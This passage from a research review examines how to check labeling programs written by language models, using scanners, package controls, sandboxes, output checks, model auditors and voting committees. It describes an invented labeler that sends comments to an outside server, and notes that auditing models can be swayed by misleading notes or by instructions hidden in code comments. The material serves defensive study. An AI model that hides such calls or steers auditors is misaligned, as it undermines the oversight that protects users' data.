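The best results come from scanners built for generated code. *Purple Llama CyberSecEval* (2023) reports that Meta's Insecure Code Detector had a precision of 96% and a recall of 79%, based on 50 hand-labeled pieces of model-written code in each programming language. Meta later used the detector in Code Shield, a filter that blocks insecure suggestions, although *CYBERSECEVAL 3* (2024) cautions that it "is not a panacea".

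*DeVAIC* (Cotroneo, De Luca and Liguori, 2024) describes a scanner for incomplete code, which language models often produce and many scanners cannot parse. Its regular expressions cover 35 types of weakness in Python. The researchers report 94% accuracy and an average scan time of 0.14 seconds per piece of code. The developers of both tools ran these evaluations themselves, and independent tests of general-purpose scanners have been much less favorable.

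In *Persistent Human Feedback, LLMs, and Static Analyzers for Secure Code Generation*, Firouzi and Ghafari (2026) had reviewers check 1,080 pieces of code from GPT-4o, each for one specific weakness, and compared the reviewers' verdicts with those of two scanners. In *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation*, Lunghi, Djire and colleagues (2026) ran Semgrep and Bandit on working Python programs from three models. The programming tasks came from several collections, including SecEvalPlus, where the weaknesses often have no recognizable pattern, and RiskyPy, which was built from tasks whose solutions scanners tend to flag.

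| Study | Scanner | Insecure programs | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Firouzi and Ghafari | CodeQL | 39% | 67% | 34% |
| Firouzi and Ghafari | Semgrep | 39% | 52% | 54% |
| Lunghi and colleagues, SecEvalPlus | Semgrep and Bandit | 62–87% | 75–83% | 4–6% |
| Lunghi and colleagues, RiskyPy | Semgrep and Bandit | 46–58% | 48–61% | 80–94% |

A scanner's precision means little without the share of all programs that were insecure. On SecEvalPlus, 83% of the programs by one model that the scanners flagged were insecure, but so were 87% of all its working programs. On RiskyPy, the scanners found most of the insecure programs, largely because they flagged at least three-quarters of all programs. RiskyPy's verdicts on which programs were insecure are also uncertain, because a language model made them and two experts who labeled a sample agreed with each other only 66% of the time.

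A program that passes a scan after repairs may be no safer than before. Lunghi and colleagues gave models the scanner's warnings and compared their results on RiskyPy with those of models that received no warnings. With the warnings, significantly more programs both worked and passed the scan in all 12 comparisons, but security improved significantly in only two. The models also followed warnings that conflicted with the task. In 79 of 83 cases in a set of web applications, they removed a network setting that the specification required, despite an instruction to put the task first.

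Most of the weaknesses found in these studies are mistakes that an attacker could exploit in ordinary software, such as inserting a user's text directly into a database command. There are few places in a keyword labeler where such mistakes could occur. In *Broken by Default* (2026), Semgrep and Bandit together caught only two of 90 mathematically proven flaws in generated code, and CodeQL caught none. That result is less relevant to labelers for the same reason, and because most of the flaws were in C, which few labeling programs use.

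Scanners are poorly suited to finding the faults that matter most in labeling code. A scanner might flag the `urlopen` call in `label_toxic` if it has a rule for network calls. It would not normally flag "gay" in a list of words or a number that depends on region, because both are normal Python. Lunghi and colleagues note that pattern-matching scanners cannot detect flaws in business logic, the rules that determine what a program decides. In a labeling program, these rules produce the labels.

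### Checking packages

A program can also be dangerous because of a package it imports. Some scanners look for malicious packages, but their results vary widely. In *Cutting the Gordian Knot* (2026), a scanner called GuardDog found 94% of the malicious Python packages in one collection but only 68% in a collection of newer ones. A new detector, PyGuard, found 94% of the newer packages. Of the 19 malicious packages that PyGuard missed in the main test, eight contained no malicious code themselves but imported another package that did, and six downloaded their malicious code only when they ran.

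Scanners that catch more malicious packages may also reject many safe ones. *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* (2026) compares detectors on 6,420 malicious and 7,288 harmless JavaScript packages. One detector caught 98.7% of the malicious packages but also flagged 86% of the harmless ones (6,234). Two others were almost always right when they flagged a package, but they missed about a third of the malicious ones.

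For labeling programs, a fixed set of packages is simpler and safer. The developer chooses a few well-known packages, installs exact versions of them in advance and does not let programs install others. If the writer model invents a package name, the import fails, even if an attacker has registered that name. OpenAI takes this approach for Python code that its customers supply to grade model output, and its *Graders* lists 16 packages with their version numbers. The packages could still be unsafe, but the developer has to check them only once rather than for every program.

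### Running the program in a sandbox

A sandbox limits what a program can reach while it runs, whatever its code looks like. The ExecJudges sandbox enforces the bans on network access, files and other programs, and limits memory to 4 GB. Each program has 5 to 30 minutes to grade all the documents for a topic, depending on the collection.

AI providers set similar limits on their customers' grading code, which does the same job as a programmatic judge. OpenAI blocks network access and limits the code to 256 KB in size, two minutes of running time, 2 GB of memory and 1 GB of disk space. Microsoft's *reinforcement fine tuning* lists the same limits on network access, code size, memory and disk space, but with one processor core instead of OpenAI's two. OpenAI is phasing out its graders and the services that use them, but the limits still show what a large provider considered sufficient for this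 kind of code.

The individual settings matter more than whether a developer uses something called a sandbox. An earlier version of Hugging Face's guide includes an example of a container, a common type of isolated environment. It limits memory, processor use and the number of processes, and it runs the code as a user with few privileges. However, it leaves the network on, although the guide recommends disabling unnecessary network access, and it passes an access token into the container. Both choices make sense for the guide's main subject, AI agents that need to call a model, but `label_toxic` could still send out every comment from inside that container.

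Developers can also limit the data a program receives. It should get a read-only copy, so that it cannot overwrite the original, and only the columns it needs. A program that judges comments does not need the commenter's region. Without that column, `label_toxic` could not apply its lower threshold to commenters in the north, though the text could still contain proxies for region, such as dialect or the name of a town.

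When the sandbox blocks an action, it should record the attempt and stop the program. Otherwise, the program might catch the error and carry on, and the developer would never learn that it had tried to contact a server.

### Accepting only valid labels

The last check is on the sandbox's output. For `label_toxic`, the surrounding code should accept exactly one label per comment, either 1, 0 or −1. A free-text explanation could carry private data into a report or instructions to a language model later in the pipeline, while a single number leaves little room for either.

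A sandboxed program could still cause harm when the developer opens its results outside the sandbox, depending on their format. Python's pickle format can store almost any object, but Hugging Face warns that loading pickled data can run arbitrary code. By default, Hugging Face's remote executors accept only JSON, a plain data format.

Developers also need to decide how to record a program's failures. OpenAI gives a grade of 0 if the code crashes or returns something invalid. That is reasonable for a quality score, where 0 is the worst result, but not for `label_toxic`, where 0 means harmless. If the sandbox blocked the network call and the system recorded every crash as 0, it would label all comments harmless. Recording crashes as abstentions would be safer, but developers should still count crashes separately, because a program that fails only on certain dialects would otherwise appear to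 abstain on them.

The ExecJudges grading formula, which sits outside the generated code, restricts the output further. For most collections, it uses four yes-or-no answers about each document: whether the document is on the subject, contains some answer, contains the exact answer and is mainly about the query. It assigns these grades:

- 0 if the document is not on the subject
- 1 if it is on the subject but contains no answer
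- 3 if it contains the exact answer and is mainly about the query
- 2 in all other cases

A program cannot return a grade of 50 or change what a 3 means, but it can still answer the questions incorrectly. A biased word list could affect those answers as it affects a label.

### `label_toxic` under these restrictions

The table shows what each restriction would do about the three faults in `label_toxic`.

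| Restriction | Call to the outside server | "gay" in the word list | Lower threshold for the north |
|---|---|---|---|
| Keywords only | Impossible to write | Allowed | Impossible to write |
| Allow-list | Rejected | Allowed | Allowed |
| Security scanner | Flagged if there is a rule for it | Allowed | Allowed |
| Sandbox without network access | Blocked | Allowed | Allowed, unless the program does not receive the region |
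| Check for valid labels | Not detected | Allowed | Allowed |

Several restrictions block the outside call, so the developer is protected even if one fails, but none of them stops the program from using the identity term. If the writer model gets a chance to repair the program, it can delete the two network lines and submit the rest. The new version would pass every check and still mark "My gay brother loved this" as toxic if the comment came from the north.

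Confinement also would not stop a line that returns 0 whenever a comment mentions a certain company, because the line needs no imports, uses no network and returns a valid label. Confinement protects the developer's computer and data, but the labels still need tests or human review.

### What the restrictions cost in accuracy

Blocking access to the network, files and other programs should not affect a keyword labeler, because it uses none of them. Restricting the form of the code could affect its performance more. The table compares hand-written rules, DataSculpt's keywords and the free-form programs that GPT-3.5 wrote for Alchemist. The scores are accuracies, except for SMS, which uses F1.

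| Dataset | Hand-written rules | DataSculpt keywords | Alchemist programs |
|---|---|---|---|
| YouTube | 0.887 | 0.896 | 0.891 |
| SMS | 0.865 | 0.821 | 0.900 |
| IMDb | 0.761 | 0.791 | 0.662 |
| Yelp | 0.847 | 0.869 | 0.575 |

Keyword rules did much better than free-form programs on the two review datasets but worse on SMS spam. The comparison is not controlled, because DataSculpt used an average of 76 to 164 rules per dataset, compared with Alchemist's ten programs, and had labeled examples to learn from. Using a stronger model to write the programs also narrows the gap, as GPT-4 did for Alchemist on Yelp. Still, these results provide no evidence that classifying short texts requires free-form code.

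DataSculpt had more trouble with relations between things in a text, where its patterns scored lower than hand-written rules on three of four tasks. On one, identifying how a chemical and a protein are related, its patterns were 27% accurate, compared with 54% for the hand-written rules. The patterns came from 2023 models, so current models may write better ones.

In ExecJudges, Agichtein and colleagues tested two of the restrictions. Their policy forbids embeddings, which represent the meaning of a text as a list of numbers. On one collection, a program allowed to use embeddings agreed slightly less with human assessors (0.606) than the standard program did (0.636). Keeping the grading formula outside the code made no significant difference compared with letting programs return a grade. But when programs could return only "relevant" or "not relevant", agreement fell by 0.113, so restricting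 the output too much can discard useful information.

The programs' larger weakness is that they match words, as in the cold bridging example. Access to the internet or to files would not widen a narrow word list. Letting the programs call a language model might help, but every item would again carry the cost of a call, and the programs would be harder to test.

Some tasks do need a model. Alchemist's bird labelers, for example, needed CLIP. A developer can run CLIP outside the sandbox and pass its ratings to the generated program as numbers. The program then needs no access to the model, the image files or the network.

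## The view that other models should do the auditing

Claude Opus 5.5 takes about a minute to write the three ExecJudges programs for a search topic, while a person would need half an hour to read them. A language model could keep up, reading every program, interpreting test results and rewriting faulty lines. Writing the 888 programs for five of the test collections cost about $56 in model calls. If auditing a program costs about as much as writing it, a model could check them all for about $56. A person paid $30 an hour would cost $4,440.

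Huang and colleagues make this argument for PAJAMA. Its judges are code, so a coding agent (a language model that can open, edit and run files) can inspect them line by line, and a bias becomes "a bug that can be patched". Their experiment and the one on ExecJudges used labeling programs. The other evidence comes from decision functions, general programming and tasks that don't involve code.

### A generator, an auditor and a refiner

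Chen and colleagues gave three roles to language models and connected them in a loop:

1. The generator writes a decision function.
2. Ordinary code runs the counterfactual test for one protected attribute and calculates the share of people whose result changes.
3. The auditor receives the function, the measured share and an explanation of what the share means. It decides whether the function is biased and gives its reasons.
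4. If the auditor finds no bias, the loop ends. Otherwise, the refiner rewrites the function to reduce the bias while keeping the logic that the task needs.
5. The test runs again on the new version, and the auditor reassesses it. After five rewrites, the loop returns the latest version, even if it is still biased.

The test has already measured the bias, so the auditor does not have to detect it by reading the code. The auditor interprets the result and explains what in the code might be responsible. The paper does not name a separate model for this role, so the same model may have written and audited the functions.

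The researchers compared the loop with three methods that use less compute. One added sample functions that had passed the bias test, and another asked the model to reason about which attributes it needed and which to avoid. The third combined the two by giving examples that included the reasoning. The table shows each method's code bias score, which is the share of 100 functions that failed the test.

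| Dataset | Attribute | Original prompt | Loop | Examples | Reasoning | Both |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Credit | Sex | 0.21 | 0.00 | 0.15 | 0.10 | 0.00 |
| Census income | Age | 0.99 | 0.47 | 0.92 | 0.89 | 0.06 |
| Census income | Sex | 0.78 | 0.04 | 0.41 | 0.05 | 0.00 |
| Census income | Race | 0.00 | 0.00 | 0.00 | 0.00 | 0.00 |
| Census income | Region | 0.00 | 0.03 | 0.00 | 0.00 | 0.00 |
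| Census income | Marital status | 0.93 | 0.06 | 0.79 | 0.08 | 0.02 |
| COMPAS | Age | 0.82 | 0.04 | 0.86 | 0.82 | 0.07 |
| COMPAS | Sex | 0.74 | 0.01 | 0.42 | 0.21 | 0.00 |
| COMPAS | Race | 0.07 | 0.00 | 0.01 | 0.00 | 0.00 |

The average score fell from 0.50 with the original prompt to 0.07 with the loop and 0.02 with examples that included reasoning. The loop did better only for age in COMPAS. It can take about a dozen model calls per function, while the prompting methods take one.

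Most of the bias that remained after the loop was related to age in the census data. Either the auditor accepted age as a reasonable predictor of income, or the refiner failed to remove its effect in five attempts. Chen and colleagues suggest that models need more guidance on attributes less widely recognized as protected. More rounds would probably not have helped much, because most of the improvement on the census data came in the first few.

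The paper's abstract concludes that bias "remains prevalent" after these measures. This is accurate for examples alone and for the loop's result on age in the census data. For the combined prompt, the paper's closing statement that bias is "not completely eliminated" fits the figures better. An even simpler prompt that named the protected attribute had already reduced all nine scores to zero. The loop also needs someone to name the attribute, because the test must specify what to change.

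None of these scores measures whether the functions are still useful, so a function that gives everyone the same answer would score zero. Chen and colleagues leave measuring usefulness to future work.

The refiner could also replace a protected attribute with a proxy. The census records have a relationship column with values that include "Husband" and "Wife". A function that switched from sex to this column would pass the test for sex. A developer who uses such a loop should therefore also check the final program's accuracy and its errors by group, on data that the loop has not used.

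### Editing PAJAMA's programs

Huang and colleagues used Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to remove PAJAMA's formatting bonuses. They also instructed it to address three other biases and to preserve each program's original purpose where possible. For each bias, they altered one of two equally good answers and recorded how a committee of eight programs judged the pair. The flip rate is the share of pairs in which the alteration changed the verdict, and the win rate is the share in which the altered answer won.

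| Alteration to one answer | Flip rate before edits | Flip rate after edits | Win rate before edits | Win rate after edits |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Decorative formatting | 23.13% | 13.74% | 48.92% | 53.28% |
| Fake or irrelevant references | 20.30% | 17.29% | 47.10% | 43.17% |
| Rewriting from a male-only perspective | 7.69% | 3.70% | 46.27% | 36.17% |
| Padding with filler text | 9.34% | 3.25% | 16.84% | 9.68% |

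The average flip rate fell from 12.09% to 7.60%. This average includes a fifth test, in which the researchers swapped the order of the two answers. The order made no difference before or after the edits because the programs score each answer separately. Without that test, the average fell from 15.1% to 9.5%.

The edits made the programs less sensitive to all four alterations, but answers with decorative formatting won 4.36 percentage points more often. The win rate depends partly on which answer the programs preferred before the alteration. The edits could have changed that, so the increase doesn't necessarily mean that the programs had come to prefer formatting.

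Judging by the figures for the male-only perspective, the agent probably changed how the programs judged ordinary answers as well as how they reacted to the rewriting. After the edits, the rewriting changed only 3.70% of verdicts, and the rewritten answer won 36.17% of the time. The programs must therefore have chosen the unrewritten version of that answer in only about 32% to 40% of pairs. Before the edits, that range was 39% to 54%.

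Huang and colleagues treat a lower win rate as better, but if two answers are equally good, a fair judge should choose each about half the time. A rate of 36% could reflect a new preference in the opposite direction. Padding is different, because a judge can reasonably mark an answer down for filler.

The instructions named the biases, so the experiment shows only that a model can edit labeling programs to reduce a bias it has been told about. It does not test whether the model would have found those biases, or unlisted ones, on its own.

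### Four attempts to correct ExecJudges

Agichtein and colleagues tried four times to correct ExecJudges, without success, by giving the writer model human labels instead of a list of known biases. The table shows how each attempt changed agreement with human assessors (Krippendorff's alpha) on data outside the correction set.

| What the model wrote or revised | Change in agreement on other data |
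|---|---|
| The shared code that turns answers into grades | −0.014 to +0.003 over four rounds |
| Guidance in its own prompt | −0.010 |
| Each program, after seeing its errors on 16 labeled passages | −0.005 to +0.006 |
| Written grading guidelines, based on ten labeled topics per year | −0.017 and −0.037 |

The third attempt lowered the error rate on the 16 passages used for the corrections from between 9% and 12% to between 3% and 4%. Agreement on other passages hardly changed, but anyone who checked only the first 16 would have thought the attempt had succeeded.

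The same kind of labels helped much more when the model saw them before writing the programs. Including 16 labeled passages per topic in the original prompt raised agreement by 0.096 to 0.166, and more than half of this gain came from the first four. The third attempt started from programs written this way, so the model had already seen the labels. The remaining errors were probably exceptions to the model's general rules, and a special rule for each one would help little with other passages.

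The edits to PAJAMA and ExecJudges also differed in difficulty. Removing a bonus for bullet points requires only finding the line and deleting it. Fixing a program that misses relevant passages requires writing a new rule to cover wording nobody has listed. A model auditor is therefore likely to be more useful for removing a bad rule than for supplying a missing one.

### How reliably models judge code

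An auditor also has to recognize bad code. In *Bias in the Loop*, Zhao, Esmaeili and Fard (2026) tested models on 5,352 pairs of answers to tasks that involved writing code, repairing code or writing tests. Each pair had one correct and one incorrect answer, and the models had to pick the better one, sometimes after reading an irrelevant note about the two.

These notes easily influenced Qwen3-4B, a small open model. The table shows its accuracy when a note described the first answer as a refined version of the second.

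| Task | Correct answer | No note | First answer described as refined |
|---|---|---|---|
| Writing code | First | 67.50% | 76.72% |
| Writing code | Second | 75.41% | 65.49% |
| Repairing code | First | 74.43% | 84.03% |
| Repairing code | Second | 79.80% | 67.54% |

The note raised accuracy when the refined answer was correct and lowered it otherwise. The effect was larger on difficult repairs, where accuracy fell from 54.52% to 36.72% when the note favored the wrong answer. Even without a note, the model was more accurate when the correct answer came second.

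A closed GPT model's accuracy at choosing the correct test also fell, from 77.46% to 62.51%, when the prompt included a distracting note about formatting and trivia. Some models also had trouble giving a usable verdict. One general Qwen setup answered in the required format only about 44% of the time, compared with about 99% for a Qwen model specialized in code.

The best current models can probably do better than these results, since the two Qwen models have only three or four billion parameters. The figures also measure how often a model picks the better of two programs, which is different from a detection rate. Picking is easier in one respect than auditing a single program, because the model knows that one of the two is wrong. An auditor of labeling code has to decide whether there is any fault at all, and may raise false alarms on clean programs.

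The experiment still suggests that, in a loop like the one Chen and colleagues built, the developer should not tell the auditor that it is looking at a refined version. Comments such as "checked for bias" could have a similar effect, so the developer can remove comments before the audit and check them separately for offensive text. This would also remove any instructions to the auditor hidden in the comments. Agichtein and colleagues mention that instructions embedded in a document can influence a model that grades it, and the same could happen with code.

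### Shared blind spots

The main objection to using models as auditors is that the auditor may miss the same problems as the model that wrote the code. If both classify "gay" as an insult, the auditor will approve the word list in `label_toxic`, the invented toxicity labeler. The risk depends on how often the two models make the same mistake and how good the auditor is overall.

Suppose that the writer introduces a certain fault with probability w, that the auditor would fail to recognize it with probability m, and that ρ is the correlation between the two events. The probability that the fault gets into a program and survives the audit is

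wm + ρ√(w(1 − w)m(1 − m)).

If the writer makes a fault in 10% of programs (w = 0.1) and the auditor misses 20% of faults on average (m = 0.2), independent errors would leave an undetected fault in 2% of programs. With a correlation of 0.5 between their errors, this would rise to 8%, because the auditor would catch only 20% of the faults that the writer makes.

Several studies have measured how strongly models' errors are correlated, but none tested code review. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) compared pairs of models on questions that both had answered incorrectly. Models often gave the same wrong answer, especially if they were accurate or shared characteristics. A model from Google and one from the company Writer, with no publicly known connection, gave the same answer to 99.87% of the questions that both got wrong. Using an auditor from a different company therefore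 does not guarantee that it will make different errors.

*The Oracle's Fingerprint* (2026) reports similar results for forecasts. On 568 questions, the errors of GPT-4o, Claude and Gemini had an average correlation of 0.77, compared with a typical range of 0.1 to 0.3 among people. Some correlation is natural in forecasting, because a surprising event makes most forecasters wrong in the same direction. Code review has no direct equivalent, so the figure may not apply to it.

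Switching to a different model can still help. *Shared Item-Level Error Limits the Aggregation of Small Language Models* (2026) examined rough numerical estimates by small models. Across four sets of results, errors in two answers from the same model correlated at 0.73 to 0.91, while errors in answers from different models correlated at 0.37 to 0.60. But models from the same family were not distinguishably more alike than models from different families. This differs from the finding that shared characteristics matter, possibly because the tasks and models were different.

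ExecJudges provides some evidence from labeling programs written by Claude Opus 5.5. Claude Sonnet 5.5, a model from the same company, graded many of the same passages directly. Of 7,402 passages from one collection, the programs graded about 570 at least two grades away from the human assessors. On 226 of these, neither Sonnet nor the two other methods in the comparison made such a large error. A model from the same family could therefore have helped find at least 40% of the programs' large errors by reading the passages.

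For example, the programs gave the cold bridging passage a 0, while Sonnet gave it a 2, the same grade as the human assessors. The error came from the programs' word-matching rules, since a related model could grade the passage correctly.

Sonnet was sometimes wrong where the programs were right. For a search about the name of a baby nurse, the assessors and the programs gave a 0 to a passage explaining that the name Fatima means "baby's nurse", but Sonnet gave it a 2. A developer who let Sonnet overrule the programs would have replaced a correct label with an incorrect one. Disagreement between a model and a program is a good reason to look at an item, but someone still has to decide which label is right.

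Disagreement among the programs is less useful. Agichtein and colleagues found no significant correlation between how often the programs for a topic disagreed and how well they matched the assessors' labels.

### Models flag labels and physicians check them

A mixed design uses models to narrow down what people need to check. *Scalable Stewardship of an LLM-Assisted Clinical Benchmark with Physician Oversight* (Ye, Tawfik and colleagues, 2025) used this design to audit MedCalc-Bench, a set of questions that require language models to calculate medical scores from patient notes. GPT-4 had extracted the facts from each note, and Python scripts had calculated the reference answers. The audited labels therefore came partly from code, although people appear to have written the scripts.

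In the first stage, Gemini 2.5 Pro checked each of the 1,047 test labels five times. It could search the web, and it saw the patient note, the extracted facts and a description of the scoring logic. A label counted as a likely error if at least four of the five runs flagged it, which happened for 279 labels (26.6%). One physician checked seven of these and agreed that all were wrong.

One of the faults was in a Python script for the Glasgow Coma Scale, a measure of consciousness. The script counted one value twice, which made the scores too high. A fault like this can affect every patient with the relevant value, just as a bad rule in a labeling program can affect every example it applies to.

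In the second stage, Gemini recalculated the answers without seeing the original labels. A new label usually required at least four of five runs to agree, and 887 questions received one. Three physicians then worked out the answers to 50 questions on which the old and new labels differed most, with one physician per question. The physicians' answers matched the new labels on 37 questions and the original labels on 10.

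The models found many errors, but the 13 mismatches show why people made the final decisions. If the researchers had accepted the new labels, about a quarter of these 50 would still have been wrong. When a physician's answer revealed a systematic mistake in Gemini's reasoning, the researchers also corrected the labels on other questions that used the same score.

The four-of-five rule is good at removing random errors. If each run independently flags a correct label 20% of the time, at least four of the five will flag it only 0.7% of the time. But the rule also misses more real errors than a single run does. If each run detects a bad label 80% of the time, at least four will flag it only 74% of the time.

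Voting does not correct errors that all the runs share. Ye and colleagues acknowledge that five runs of one model could all misinterpret a scoring rule in the same way. The physicians would be unlikely to notice, because they looked mainly at labels on which the old and new answers disagreed, and the two would match if Gemini had repeated GPT-4's mistake.

For labeling programs, this design could reduce the reading. If models flagged a quarter of the 888 ExecJudges programs, people would have 222 to read, which would take 37 hours instead of 148. They should also read a random sample of the programs that the models passed, so that the developer can estimate how many faults the models missed.

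### Testing auditors from different families

To find out whether a model from a different family makes a better auditor, researchers could have one model from each of four families write labeling programs for the same tasks. They would use tests on trusted labels, then specialist review, to identify 100 faulty and 100 clean programs from each model. One model from each family would then audit all 800 programs without being told which model wrote each one or how many were faulty.

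The faults should be mistakes the writers made themselves. Planted faults are useful for measuring human reviewers, but they would not show whether an auditor overlooks the mistakes its own family tends to make. A smaller set of planted faults could serve as a control, since the auditor's family should not affect how often it finds them.

A simple comparison of detection rates could be misleading, because some auditors are better than others and some writers' faults are easier to find. The researchers could account for both with

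log(p / (1 − p)) = aᵢ + bⱼ + γsᵢⱼ,

where p is the probability that auditor i detects a fault by writer j, aᵢ is the auditor's skill, and bⱼ reflects how easy the writer's faults are to find. The value of sᵢⱼ is 1 if both models come from the same family and 0 otherwise. A negative γ would mean that models are worse at finding their own family's faults.

Auditors from the writer's model family would give 400 verdicts on the 400 faulty programs, and other auditors would give 1,200. To distinguish a detection rate of 60% from one of 70%, the researchers would need about 353 verdicts in each group if the verdicts were independent. All four auditors would read the same programs, so the verdicts would not be fully independent, and the analysis would have to account for this. At about six cents per audit, the 3,200 audits would cost roughly $200. Confirming the faults would cost much more because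 it requires specialists.

The researchers could repeat the audits with counterfactual test results included, as in the loop by Chen and colleagues. Including these results might matter more than the choice of model family, because the auditor would no longer have to notice the bias by itself. The researchers should also report which faults each auditor missed. If all four miss the same ones, switching to an auditor from another family would not help, and the developer would need better tests or human reviewers for those faults.

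## Does combining several programs remove a bias or keep it?

Labeling systems rarely rely on a single program. Alchemist merges votes from ten programs, PAJAMA merges votes from 8 to 21, and ExecJudges averages three grades. If merging cancels the faults of individual programs, a developer can tolerate a few bad ones and spend less time auditing each. But if most of the programs share a fault, merging doesn't remove it, and the developer has to audit the programs as a group.

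Experiments on labeling programs show how combining them affects accuracy. Evidence on shared faults comes mostly from general programming, and evidence on fairness from labeling rules that language models did not write.

### What voting does to errors

Suppose that three programs each mislabel 10% of items and that their errors are independent. A majority vote is wrong only if at least two of them are wrong, which happens with probability

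3 × 0.1² × 0.9 + 0.1³ = 0.028, or 2.8%.

With five such programs, the figure is 0.9%.

Whether combining several programs removes a bias depends on whether their errors are independent. Suppose the programs label toxic comments, and some of them count "gay" as an insult, as `label_toxic` does. Those programs mislabel every harmless comment that contains the word, while the others mislabel 10% of such comments.

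| Programs with the biased word | Average error of one program on these comments | Error after a majority vote |
|---|---|---|
| None | 10% | 2.8% |
| One of three | 40% | 19% |
| Two of three | 70% | 100% |
| All three | 100% | 100% |

When programs vote on labels, the others usually outvote a single biased program, but two biased programs always win, and the merged labels are then worse than those of a program picked at random.

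Overall accuracy can improve even when voting leaves a shared bias in place. Suppose all three programs contain the word, the affected comments make up 2% of the data, and the programs err independently on 10% of the rest. Voting cuts the total error from 11.8% to 4.7% but still mislabels every affected comment. These comments account for 42% of all errors, up from 17%.

The outcome also depends on how often the writer model produces biased programs. If a share b of its programs are biased, a committee of three has a biased majority with probability 3b² − 2b³. This is less than b when b is below one half and more than b when it is above. In the experiment by Chen and colleagues, 21% of GPT-4o's credit functions and 78% of its census functions failed the test for sex. Committees of three would have a biased majority 11% of the time for credit and 88% for census. But those were decision functions,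 and two functions can be biased against different people, so their effects may partly cancel.

### How a label model can reward a shared mistake

Without gold labels, a label model infers each program's reliability from how often the programs agree. If programs i and j have accuracies aᵢ and aⱼ and make independent errors, they agree on a share gᵢⱼ of items, where

2gᵢⱼ − 1 = (2aᵢ − 1)(2aⱼ − 1).

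Three programs give three equations, enough to solve for all three accuracies. In the invented example below, programs X and Y contain the biased word and program Z does not.

| Comments | Number | X | Y | Z |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Harmless, with "gay" | 20 | Wrong | Wrong | Right |
| Other | 5 | Wrong | Right | Right |
| Other | 5 | Right | Wrong | Right |
| Other | 5 | Right | Right | Wrong |
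| Other | 65 | Right | Right | Right |

X and Y agree on 90% of the comments, and each agrees with Z on 70%. Solving the equations gives estimated accuracies of 95% for X and Y and 72% for Z, but the true accuracies are nearly the reverse, at 75% for X and Y and 95% for Z.

If toxic and harmless comments are equally common, the label model gives each of the 20 harmless comments a 99% probability of being toxic. With weights based on the true accuracies, the probability would be 32%, and the merged labels would be correct. Gold labels can therefore prevent this error, but they help less when the fault is rare. If only 2 of the 100 comments contained the word, X and Y would be nearly as accurate as Z overall and would outvote it even with the correct weights.

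Later safeguards can also miss a wrong label when the committee is confident in it. PAJAMA sends a pair of answers to a language model when the committee's verdict is uncertain, but a shared bias may not make the verdict uncertain. Huang and colleagues compared this rule with an ideal one that sends only the pairs the programs got wrong. The ideal rule did better, and part of the gap may come from mistakes the committee was confident about.

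*CARE* addresses shared errors in panels of language-model judges, where majority voting and averaging can amplify them. It separates links between particular judges from hidden factors that influence many judges, such as the true quality of an answer or a common preference for long ones. It normally treats the strongest shared factor as quality. The method reduced error by up to 26.8% across 12 benchmarks. But if nearly every judge has the same strong bias, it could treat that bias as quality. One of the paper's suggested safeguards is a small set of items rated by people.

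### What merging adds in labeling systems

Alchemist provides some evidence that varied programs help. Huang and colleagues pooled programs written from different prompts, some with extra keywords, examples or labeling rules, and increased the number of programs per kind of prompt from four to nine. The merged labels improved on all three datasets tested, which covered spam messages and reviews. Because the total number of programs also grew, the experiment does not separate the benefit of variety from the benefit of having more programs.

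The gain was smaller in ExecJudges, where Agichtein and colleagues found that agreement with human assessors rose by 0.016 to 0.031 when they went from one program to three. Most of that gain came from the second program, and the gain beyond three programs was smaller than the difference between two rewrites of the same program. All the programs for a topic came from one model and one prompt. Averaging could not correct the cold bridging error, because every program made it.

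Huang and colleagues drew committees at random from PAJAMA's programs and measured their average accuracy across five datasets. For comparison, the last column below shows the accuracy a majority vote would achieve if every program were right 62.1% of the time and their errors were independent.

| Programs | Measured accuracy | Accuracy with independent errors |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 62.1% | 62.1% |
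| 3 | 67.8% | 67.8% |
| 5 | 68.5% | 71.8% |
| 20 | 71.1% | About 86% |
| 50 | 71.4% | About 96% |

The calculation is rough because programs and datasets differ, and some reference labels may be wrong. Still, the large gap at 50 programs suggests that the programs make many of the same mistakes, which adding more programs does not correct. Selecting programs helped more than adding them, since PAJAMA's selected committees reached 78.1%.

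None of these figures measures bias against a group. The nearest evidence is PAJAMA's test with answers rewritten from a male-only perspective. Huang and colleagues gave the same test to nine language-model judges, and eight of those judges changed their verdicts less often than the committee of eight programs did. Combining programs therefore did not remove the sensitivity to gendered wording. The paper gives no figures for single programs, so it is unclear whether combining them reduced it.

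Alchemist's bird labelers have a similar problem, although the groups are not groups of people. Each labeler that used CLIP's ratings combined ten programs, but its accuracy on the worst group was still far below its average accuracy.

### Do programs from different models fail together?

Software engineers have studied this question for decades through N-version programming, in which several teams write the same program and the system takes a majority vote. In 1986, Knight and Leveson tested the idea with 27 programmers, who each wrote code to decide whether to launch an interceptor missile. The programs failed on the same inputs much more often than expected by chance.

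*N-Version Programming with Coding Agents* (Ron, Baudry and Monperrus, 2026) repeated the experiment with five AI coding tools, running 23 models, which wrote programs in three programming languages. Of 69 attempts, 48 passed an entry test and then ran on a million random inputs. At least two programs failed together on 429 inputs, compared with about 115 expected if the programs had failed independently.

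Many of the failures came from the same geometry mistake. The task was to find the smallest circle that contains three points, but many programs calculated the circle that passes through all three, which can be larger. The mistake appeared in all three languages and in programs from several tools.

Voting still helped when Ron and colleagues tested every possible committee of three programs. The average number of failures fell from 387 for single programs to 131 for committees. More than half of the single-program average came from one program that failed 10,469 times, which the other two members of a committee could usually outvote. About 68% of the committees never failed, but the rest failed on about 416 inputs on average. As in the example with the biased word, voting removed a fault unless two members shared it, in which case the fault remained almost intact.

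*A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code* (Nogueira, Pattabiraman and colleagues, 2026) covered more tasks but used older and mostly smaller models. Twelve models wrote solutions to 224 contest problems in five programming languages. The researchers measured the improvement from majority voting as a share of the improvement expected if the models' errors were independent.

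| Programs in the committee | Three programs | Five programs |
|---|---|---|
| From one model | 27% | 24% |
| From at least two models | 44% | 44% |
| From one style of prompt | 41% | 42% |
| From at least two styles of prompt | 44% | 44% |

Mixing models helped, but it achieved less than half of the possible improvement. Changing the prompt made little difference, even though one prompt style asked for unconventional solutions. Shared failures were more pronounced on edge cases, such as inputs at the limits of what the problem allows. Comments in a rare dialect might be a similar case for a labeling program, but the study did not test such inputs.

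Toxicity has no exact answers, unlike contest problems and missile rules. Programs that label toxic comments could share more faults than programs for those tasks, because the models that write them may have learned the same associations between words and groups. They could also share fewer, because there are many ways to recognize an insult.

### Fairness research on weak supervision

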